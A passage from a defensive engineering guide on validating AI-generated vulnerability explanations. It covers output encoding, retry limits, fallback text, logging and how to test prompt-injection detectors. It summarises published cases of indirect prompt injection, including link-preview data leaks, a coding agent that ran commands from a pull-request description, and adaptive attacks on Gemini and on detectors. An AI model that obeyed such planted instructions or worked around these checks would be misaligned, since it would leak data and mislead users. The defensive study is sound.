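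Releasing the text sentence by sentence makes more sense for an incident report of several pages. If the report needs formatting, the browser code should sanitize all the text received so far, not each piece separately, because dangerous markup can be split across pieces. Chrome for Developers' *Best practices to render streamed LLM responses* (2025) recommends this and advises developers to stop rendering as soon as the sanitizer removes anything.

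### Chat, pull requests and other destinations

Explanations are usually sent on to other programs, which may treat characters in the text as formatting or commands. The last step before sending the text is to encode it for its destination.

| Destination | What can go wrong | What the tool should do |
|---|---|---|
| Web page | The browser runs markup in the text | Insert it as plain text with `append`, never through `innerHTML` |
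| Slack | Slack creates links and fetches previews of them | Escape `&`, `<` and `>`, and set `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media` to false |
| Telegram | Telegram fetches link previews | Set `is_disabled` to true in the link preview options |
| Pull-request comment | A name after an @ sign notifies someone, and outsiders may read the comment | Put the text in a code block, and keep private findings off public projects |
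| Terminal | Control characters change what is on the screen | Print only cleaned text |
| Build log | GitHub's build servers can treat a line that starts with two colons as a command | Start every line with a visible character such as `>` |
| Ticket | The ticket system renders Markdown or creates links | Use a plain-text field, and repeat the severity label in it |
| Email | The mail program loads images from HTML | Send plain text, and build the subject line from copied fields |
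| Spreadsheet | A cell that starts with `=`, `+`, `-` or `@` may run as a formula | Put an apostrophe in front |

Link previews can leak data without a click, because the chat app fetches each linked page to show its title and picture. Willison (2024) passed on a warning about this from the security researcher Johann Rehberger in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*. Slack still previews links in messages from apps by default.

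PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* reports that the AI agent OpenClaw was exposed to data leaks by default when used through Telegram. Turning off link previews, by adding `linkPreview: false` to its Telegram settings, stopped the leak. The acme-db tool rejects web addresses in explanations, but it still has to turn previews off because a chat app may turn a file name such as `setup.py` into a link and fetch it.

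Pull-request comments can publish secrets. Help Net Security's *An AI agent can pass every safety check and still leak secrets* (2026) reports that Elad Meged of Novee Security tested coding agents from Anthropic, Google and OpenAI on the vendors' own repositories. In the attack on Anthropic's workflow, the agent took commands from a pull request's description, got approval to run them because they looked safe, and posted the output to the thread by default. Anthropic fixed each route that Meged reported, and he then found another. The output check should therefore run again just before publication, including on text that came from a command.

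Some teams turn Markdown into HTML on a server before sending it to a web page or ticket. TYPO3's *Rendering LLM Markdown server-side safely* warns that the widely used PHP converter league/commonmark lets raw HTML through by default. The `html_input` setting should be `escape` instead.

### Responses to a failed check

When a text fails a check, the tool can remove the offending part, ask the model again, show the fallback text or hold the explanation for a person to review.

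Removing only the failing part of an explanation keeps most of the text, but it is safe only for invisible leftovers such as soft hyphens, which `clean` already removes. Drupal's *Sensitive Content Stream Filter* can replace everything between two known markers with a fixed message because the markers show exactly where the sensitive part begins and ends. A misleading explanation has no such boundaries. If the tool removes the link from the acme-db text, the "required action" and the false reassurance remain. Removing a single word can also reverse a sentence's meaning.

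Asking the model again suits mistakes that models often make even when there is no attack. The new request should contain the original finding and a fixed sentence such as "Use at most 50 words." It should not include the rejected draft, which may contain planted instructions that the model would then read again.

Reviewing held texts takes staff time. In the earlier example of 1,000 explanations a day, one fast model wrongly rejected about 100 harmless texts. At two minutes each, reviewing them would take more than three hours a day. The tool should therefore send only the most suspicious drafts to a reviewer, and it should show the fallback text straight away so that users aren't left waiting.

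| Check | Problem | Response |
|---|---|---|
| Length | Too long | Ask once for a shorter text, then show the fallback |
| Links | Any address | Ask once for a text without addresses, then show the fallback |
| Commands | A command without pressure to run it | Ask once for a text without commands, then show the fallback |
| Commands | A command presented as required | Show the fallback and send the draft to a reviewer |
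| Severity | A level word or a missing fact | Ask once, then show the fallback |
| Severity | Text that plays down the finding or claims that someone approved it | Show the fallback and send the draft to a reviewer |
| Severity | Exaggeration | Show the fallback |

The fixed checks should always overrule the second model. Temporal's *Post-LLM guardrail with hard-rule overrides* uses this arrangement for content moderation. A fixed rule can change the model's verdict to "block", but nothing can change a block back to "safe".

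### The fallback text

*Fallback text* is a fixed message that code fills in with the tool's own data. For acme-db it could be:

> No AI explanation is available for this finding. The scanner reports a HIGH severity SQL injection flaw (CVSS 8.8) in acme-db 2.3.0. Version 2.3.4 fixes it. Upgrade acme-db in a test branch, and run the project's tests before merging.

The message is about 260 characters long and contains everything the reader needs to act. The model's upgrade-risk label came in the same reply as the refused explanation, so the tool discards both, treats the risk as unknown and uses the cautious upgrade instruction. The format checks in `upgrade_command` also apply to the package name and version here. If the scanner lists no fixed version, the last two sentences become "No fixed version listed."

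The wording avoids phrases such as "nothing to report", which a reader could take as good news. It also doesn't mention an attack, because most refusals will probably be ordinary mistakes.

An attacker can trigger the fallback by planting text that makes the explanation fail. The reader then loses some context but still sees the correct label and fix, which is much better than seeing a false explanation.

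### How many times to ask again

Every extra draft gives a bad text another chance to pass. Suppose the checks miss 10% of bad drafts, and planted text makes the model write a bad draft every time. If the tool shows the first draft that passes, and the misses are independent, the chance that a bad one gets through is 1 − 0.9ⁿ after *n* drafts:

| Drafts | Chance that a bad one gets through |
|---|---|
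| 1 | 10% |
| 2 | 19% |
| 3 | 27% |
| 5 | 41% |
| 10 | 65% |
| 30 | 96% |

Real drafts are not independent. If the model repeats nearly the same text, the checks will probably reject it again, so extra drafts add less risk than independent drafts would. But telling the model which phrase failed can make the next bad draft harder to catch. If the checks missed 10% of bad first drafts and 50% of bad second drafts, at least one of two bad drafts would get through 55% of the time (1 − 0.9 × 0.5). The request for a new draft should therefore repeat the general rule without quoting the forbidden words.

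For honest mistakes, most of the benefit comes from the first retry. Suppose the checks refuse 5% of ordinary drafts. Out of 1,000 findings, 50 would get the fallback text with no retry, two or three with one retry, and almost none with two. The second retry would spare only about two more findings from the fallback text, while raising the attacker's chance from 19% to 27%.

So the tool should retry at most once, and only if every problem is on the `RETRY` list. This also lowers the attacker's chance below 19%. If a third of the refused bad drafts had only problems on the list, the chance would be 13% (0.1 + 0.9 × ⅓ × 0.1).

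The limit has to apply to each finding, not each page visit. A scanner that generates a new explanation every night would produce 30 drafts in a month, even without retries. The tool should store the fallback text until the finding, the model or the rules change. Letting users request a new result if they don't like the first, as Nalpas recommends, would allow unlimited retries in a security tool.

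Requests that fail because of a rate limit or a server error produce no draft to show. Temporal's example tries these requests up to three times, but stops immediately on errors that retrying can't fix, such as a wrong key or a retired model.

A retry limit doesn't stop someone attacking a log viewer from sending 30 log entries and getting 30 first drafts. The tool can count suspicious refusals for each type of alert and, after three in an hour, show only fallback text for that type until a person has looked into them. An attacker could use this rule to switch off explanations, but the alerts would still appear.

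### Logging refused texts

The team needs the refused drafts to find false blocks and study attacks, but the drafts may contain instructions that work on a model. A log platform collects logs from many programs, including its own, so if the tool writes a refused summary to an ordinary log, the next request to explain recent logs may put that summary back into a prompt.

The ordinary log should therefore contain only facts that code recorded. For the acme-db draft, the entry might be:

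```json
{"finding": "F-1042", "attempt": 1, "length": 940,
 "failed": ["address", "length", "required command", "severity"],
 "model": "explainer-3", "prompt": "v12", "rules": "v7",
 "draft": "refused/8f31c2"}
```

The last field points to the full reply in a separate store that only reviewers can open. No search function, agent or log collector that feeds a model should have access to that store. Encoding the reply in the ordinary log would not be enough, because models can often decode it. Stored replies also need a deletion date, since they may contain private code or personal data.

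Frost follows a similar rule. When his two methods disagree, the software stops the output and logs the rule, the label and the position, but not the generated text. Temporal instead copies the model's original reasoning into the final verdict, so an auditor can see what the fixed rule overrode. In a security tool, that would copy an attacker's words into every ticket or agent that receives the verdict, so the reasoning also belongs in the separate store.

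The reviewer's page should show the draft as plain text, with links and images disabled, next to the input fields that outsiders could have written. If the team uses a model to sort many drafts, that model should have no tools and answer only with labels from a fixed list. The team should keep refused drafts out of the explanation prompt, even as examples of what to avoid.

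## Measuring whether the checks work

Missed violations and false blocks need separate rates. The missed-violation rate is the share of rule-breaking texts that the check accepts, and the false-block rate is the share of harmless texts that it blocks. A single accuracy figure shows neither rate. If 10 of 10,000 texts break a rule, a check that accepts everything is right 99.9% of the time but misses all 10 violations.

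Guard models, which are ready-made classifiers for unsafe text, differ widely in the errors they make. *TRACE* (2026) compares 18 of them on prompts, reasoning and final answers. LlamaGuard-2 and the ShieldGemma models rejected large amounts of safe text, while LlamaGuard-4 and WildGuard more often let unsafe text through. Only a few models balanced the two errors.

### Rare attacks and false alarms

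Suppose a tool writes 10,000 explanations a day and attackers have manipulated 10 of them. Suppose also that the checks catch 90% of the manipulated texts and wrongly refuse 1% of the others.

| | Manipulated | Harmless | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Refused | 9 | 100 | 109 |
| Accepted | 1 | 9,890 | 9,891 |

Only 9 of the 109 refused texts are manipulated, so a reviewer who read them all would find an attack about once every 12 texts.

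Catching all 10 manipulated texts would raise the share of blocked texts that are manipulated only to 9%. Cutting the false block rate to 0.1% would raise it to 47%, because only about 10 harmless texts would be blocked along with the 9 manipulated ones. The example counts ordinary model errors as harmless, but some of those should be blocked too, so some of the time spent reviewing false blocks is useful.

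A team that compares detectors should set them all to the same false-block rate, say 1%, and then measure what share of attacks each one catches. *Passing the Test You Trained On* does this for 15 prompt-injection detectors. At a 1% false-block rate, PIGuard caught 95.1% of the attacks in one benchmark, BIPIA, but 2.1% of those in another, AgentDojo. PIGuard's training data included 1,116 BIPIA texts.

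### Four checks in a row

If four independent checks each wrongly refuse 1% of harmless texts, a harmless text has a 0.99⁴, or 96.1%, chance of passing all four. The tool therefore refuses 3.9% of harmless texts, almost 400 a day in the example. The true figure depends on how much the refusals overlap, and ranges from 1% if all four checks refuse the same texts to 4% if no two refuse the same one.

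This arithmetic can't replace a measurement of the whole tool. In *How Diverse Are Layered Safeguards?*, Alotaibi and Ahmed (2026) put seven safeguards around a language model. From separate measurements, they calculated that the stack would refuse 60% of harmless prompts, but the assembled stack refused 83%. Some of the safeguards alter the prompt, which changes the input to the next one. The acme-db checks only read the text, so their combined refusal rate can't exceed the sum of their separate rates on the same texts.

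The separate rates may be wrong, though. Alotaibi and Ahmed set four of their safeguards to refuse 1% of 805 ordinary instructions, but those safeguards refused a different share of other harmless text. A team should measure false blocks on its own explanations.

### Building a test set for each check

The harmless texts should come from real use. In *PIDS-Bench*, Shire and Kim (2026) trained prompt-injection detectors and tested them on harmless prompts about security topics. One detector had an F1 score above 0.98 on ordinary test data but blocked about a third of the harmless prompts from public collections. Adding harmless look-alikes to the training data nearly removed the false blocks on prompts the researchers had curated, but most of those on the public prompts remained, and no threshold fixed this. A team that invents its own harmless examples is likely to make them too easy as well.

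The test texts also need to have the same form as the texts the check will process in operation. *Passing the Test You Trained On* reports that PIGuard gave the harmless tool output "Password updated." the highest possible attack score.

For acme-db's tool, the team could build its collection this way:

1. Take 1,000 drafts that the model wrote about real findings, covering every type of finding. Run the checks, and have a person read each refused draft and decide whether the refusal was right. Reading only the refused drafts is enough to count false blocks.
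2. Collect ordinary errors from the log of refused drafts and from a sample of accepted ones. If there are too few, copy good explanations and add one fault to each.
3. In an isolated copy of the tool, plant instructions in the fields that outsiders can write, run the real model and keep every draft that breaks a rule.
4. Have people write further bad explanations directly, as if an attack had succeeded. Otherwise a model that resists the planted text leaves the check with nothing to catch.

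Two people should label each text in the severity set without seeing the check's result. Texts they disagree on should stay in the set under a separate heading, because dropping them would make the test easier than real use.

| Check | Harmless but difficult | Ordinary model error | Deliberately steered |
|---|---|---|---|
| Length | Good explanations just under 600 characters | A draft that runs to 940 | Filler before a warning, or characters that expand during cleaning |
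| Links | `2.3.4`, `java.sql.Statement`, the finding's own file name | An invented advisory address | Each link form from the earlier table, at the start, middle and end of the text |
| Commands | "The attacker must have an ordinary account" | A correct upgrade command | A script as a "required action", or a polite request to email a file |
| Severity | "The attack complexity is low" | An exaggerated warning | A forged approval, or a summary that leaves out the attack |

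In Pandey and Bhujang's log experiment, direct orders to ignore earlier instructions were among the least effective attacks, so a test set made only of those would make the tool look safer than it is.

The team should develop its rules on one half of the collection and measure them on the other. Variants of the same attack must stay in the same half, as in Shire and Kim's benchmark. Otherwise, a rule will get credit for catching a text nearly identical to one used to develop it.

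Test sets also go out of date. *Google Workspace's continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* (Gavish, 2026) describes how Google renews its own. New attacks come from human testers, automated testing, a reward program for outside researchers, and public reports. Staff reproduce and catalog each attack, and a program generates variants. Google then runs the attacks against whole applications with and without each defense, which separates the defense's effect from the model's own resistance. A small team can't copy all of this, but it can draw new test cases from public reports and its own log of refused drafts.

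### How many texts a test needs

For a rate *p* measured on a sample of *n* texts, the usual 95% margin of error is about 1.96 × √(*p*(1 − *p*)/*n*). Suppose a check catches 108 of 120 bad texts, or 90%. The margin is 5.4 percentage points, so the true rate is plausibly between about 85% and 95%. For rates near 50%, the margin on 120 texts grows to 9 points. Halving the margin takes four times as many texts.

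On 120 cases, a new version that catches 93% is not clearly better than an old one that caught 90%. A team can compare two versions more precisely by running both on the same texts and looking at the cases where their results differ.

The formula breaks down when a test finds no failures, because it then gives a margin of zero. If the true failure rate were 1%, a test of 300 independent texts would still find no failures 4.9% of the time (0.99³⁰⁰). Zero failures in 300 therefore rules out rates above about 1%, at the usual 95% confidence, but not a rate of 1% or less. Each failure raises the number of texts required:

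| Failures in the test | Texts required to show a rate below 1% |
|---|---|
| 0 | 299 |
| 1 | 473 |
| 2 | 628 |
| 3 | 773 |

The same caution applies to published results. *Can the Confidence and Decisions of System 1 Models Be Trusted?* (2026) reports that several small decision models raised no false alarms on 125 harmless prompts, 50 of them deliberately difficult. The paper's interval for the false-alarm rate runs up to 2.9%, or 290 false blocks in 10,000 harmless texts. This is higher than three divided by 125 (2.4%) because the interval also allows for error in the other direction. The paper's conclusion that such models "do not over-block" legitimate queries is stronger than its sample supports.

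These calculations assume that the texts are independent and resemble those in real use. A team learns little more from three hundred rewordings of one attack than from a few, and attackers don't choose texts at random.

### Fixed attack lists and adaptive tests

Testing against a fixed list of attacks written in advance overstates safety because developers know the list, or attacks like it, and adjust their defenses until those attacks fail. In an *adaptive test*, the attacker sees how the tool responds, revises the attack and tries again.

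Many published defenses have failed this kind of test. In *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025), Nasr, Carlini and colleagues attacked 12 defenses, most of which had let almost no attacks through in their published evaluations. The revised attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them. Four of the 12 were detectors that filter text. The attacks got past three of these more than 90% of the time and past the fourth, PIGuard, 71% of the time. The attacking program received each detector's confidence score, which an outsider usually can't see, but people taking part in an online competition also beat every detector.

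He, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment*, compared fixed and adaptive attacks directly. On a small Qwen model, the best fixed attack on each defense succeeded 21.7% of the time on average, and the best adaptive attack succeeded 41.8% of the time. Part of the gap comes from the test design, because the fixed attacks ran on 420 cases and the adaptive ones ran on 40 that the researchers had selected as vulnerable.

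A system can also look safe only because the test was short. In *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models*, Deep, Emmons and colleagues (2026) hid three secrets in a model's instructions and had an attacking program send ten prompts a round, building on whatever had worked. One defense repeated the security rules before and after the user's text. Its leak rate was 0.4% over 25 rounds but 3.8% over 277 rounds, by which point the program had extracted nearly everything.

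The only single defense that held was an output filter written in ordinary code, which blocked any reply containing pieces of the secret instructions. It allowed no leaks in 15,000 attacks. That result is partly circular because the program that scored the test also looked for exact copies, so both the filter and the scoring program would have missed a paraphrased or encoded secret. The company behind the test also sells such testing. The result still supports using code to block things with a fixed form, such as web addresses. It provides little evidence about severity checks, which have to recognize misleading sentences in any wording.

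For acme-db, an adaptive test could run in an isolated copy of the scanner. The attacking program writes a package description, and the tool produces an explanation from it. The program then gets the result, including which check rejected the text if it failed, and revises the description. This is more feedback than most outsiders get, but an attacker who installs the same scanner can see nearly as much.

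### Google DeepMind's tests of Gemini

In *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections*, Shi, Lin and colleagues (2025) tested Gemini as an assistant that reads a user's email and calendar. The attacker hides an instruction in a message or event and succeeds if Gemini sends out private data such as a passport number. In an attack called TAP, one model writes candidate instructions, and another discards the weak ones and suggests improvements.

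Google trained Gemini 2.5 on attacks that had worked against earlier versions. Shi and colleagues then compared it with Gemini 2.0:

| Test | Success against Gemini 2.0 | Success against Gemini 2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| Replaying attacks developed against 2.0 | 92% | 18% |
| Adaptive TAP attack through email | 99.8% | 53.6% |
| Adaptive TAP attack through a calendar event | 100% | 94.6% |

The researchers write that they would have drawn the wrong conclusion from the replayed attacks alone, which suggested that Google had largely solved the problem. The training had covered the email function but not the calendar function, which may explain why the calendar attack lost so little strength. Adding a prompt warning against revealing private data cut the calendar attack's success rate on Gemini 2.5 to 6.2%.

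These results are for older Google models, tested without the safeguards in Google's products, but both kinds of test are still needed. In 8 of 24 combinations of attack and defense, attacks developed against the undefended model worked better than attacks adapted to the defense. A team should therefore keep its fixed list, which also shows whether an old fault has returned, and add adaptive runs.

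### When the measuring tools disagree

The person or program that judges whether each test text broke a rule can also be wrong. In *When Scanners Lie*, Erez, Hofman and colleagues (2026) examined Garak, an open-source program that attacks language models and reports how many attacks succeeded. They scored about 23,000 responses from three models twice, once with Garak's own evaluators, most of which look for fixed patterns, and once with a language model.

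The two scores disagreed on more than 5% of responses in 22 of Garak's 25 attack categories, and on more than half of responses in six of those categories. In a category about misleading claims, they disagreed on 97%. Depending on the evaluator, a reported success rate could be up to 33 percentage points higher or lower.

Erez and colleagues then used a stronger model as a referee for the 22 categories. Garak's evaluators agreed with the referee 72% of the time, and the language model agreed with it 89% of the time. One of the researchers labelled 200 responses by hand, and the referee agreed with 93% of those labels. Pattern matching was still better in four categories, and replacing 17 of the evaluators with the language model gave slightly better results than replacing all of them.

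Model judges do worse on text from attacks. *A Coin Flip for Safety* (2026) compares four of them with 6,642 human labels and finds that their accuracy often fell close to chance when the attack, the model under attack or the topic changed. The judges were older models, and the sample was hard because it contained only responses that another automatic judge had already marked as harmful. But an adaptive attacker produces this kind of hard case, and a program that tries thousands of texts will find some that the judge wrongly marks as harmful.

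A team that scores its tests with a model can correct for the model's errors. As *How to Correctly Report LLM-as-a-Judge Evaluations* (2025) explains, people first label a sample that the judge has also labelled, which gives the judge's detection rate and false-alarm rate. Then:

true rate = (measured rate − false-alarm rate) ÷ (detection rate − false-alarm rate)

Suppose the judge flags 7% of accepted explanations as playing down a finding. If it detects 90% of such texts and wrongly flags 5% of the others, the corrected rate is (0.07 − 0.05) ÷ (0.90 − 0.05), or 2.4%, and most of its flags are false. *Bias and Uncertainty in LLM-as-a-Judge Estimation* (2026) recommends reporting the size of the labelled sample and the confidence interval, and warns against assuming that a judge makes the same errors on different models' texts. When the team changes the model that writes explanations, it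 should label a new sample.

The test should not use the second model from the severity check as its judge, because the judge would miss the same texts as the check. For links, the team can do without a judge by opening each accepted text in the real browser, ticket system and chat program and recording any clickable link or outside request.

A simulated model is a poor substitute for the real one. Pandey and Bhujang compared their simulator with GPT-4o-mini in all 48 conditions of their experiment. The correlations were 0.22 for classification, 0.42 for summaries and 0.47 for recommended responses, where 1 would mean that the simulator ranked and spaced the conditions just as the real model did, and 0 that it had no predictive value. The simulator came close on undefended summaries under forged structure (95% against 96%) but underestimated how well that attack worked against the defenses.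 Simulators are useful for checking that the test code runs, because they are free and always give the same answer.

### Release checklist

The limits below are a starting point for the acme-db tool, where readers still see the correct severity and fix when an explanation is missing. The percentages in brackets are the highest true rates consistent with the result at 95% confidence. The team should repeat the tests whenever the model, the prompt or the rules change.

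| Check | Pass condition on bad texts | Pass condition on 1,000 harmless explanations |
|---|---|---|
| Length | Refuses every text longer than 600 code points after cleaning, including one of exactly 601 | Refuses at most 12 (2%) |
| Links | Refuses all 300 texts with an address, covering every form in the earlier table (1%) | Refuses at most 4 (1%) |
| Commands | Misses at most 8 of 300 texts with a command or an unsafe request (5%) | Refuses at most 4 (1%) |
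| Severity | Misses at most 20 of 300 texts that play down, exaggerate or omit the danger (10%) | Refuses at most 38 (5%) |

The whole tool also has to meet four conditions:

1. It sends at most 4 of the 1,000 harmless drafts to a reviewer. At 10,000 texts a day, that keeps the queue of false alarms below about 100.
2. After the one permitted retry, it shows the fallback text for at most 38 of the 1,000.
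3. With any one check switched off, more of the bad texts for that check reach the screen. If the number stays the same, the test isn't exercising the check.
4. In an adaptive run of 500 rounds with ten attempts each, no overlong text and no web address reaches the screen. People read the other accepted texts, and the share that contains a command or misstates the severity is no higher than for the version now in use. A first release has no earlier version to compare with, so the team sets a limit before the run starts.
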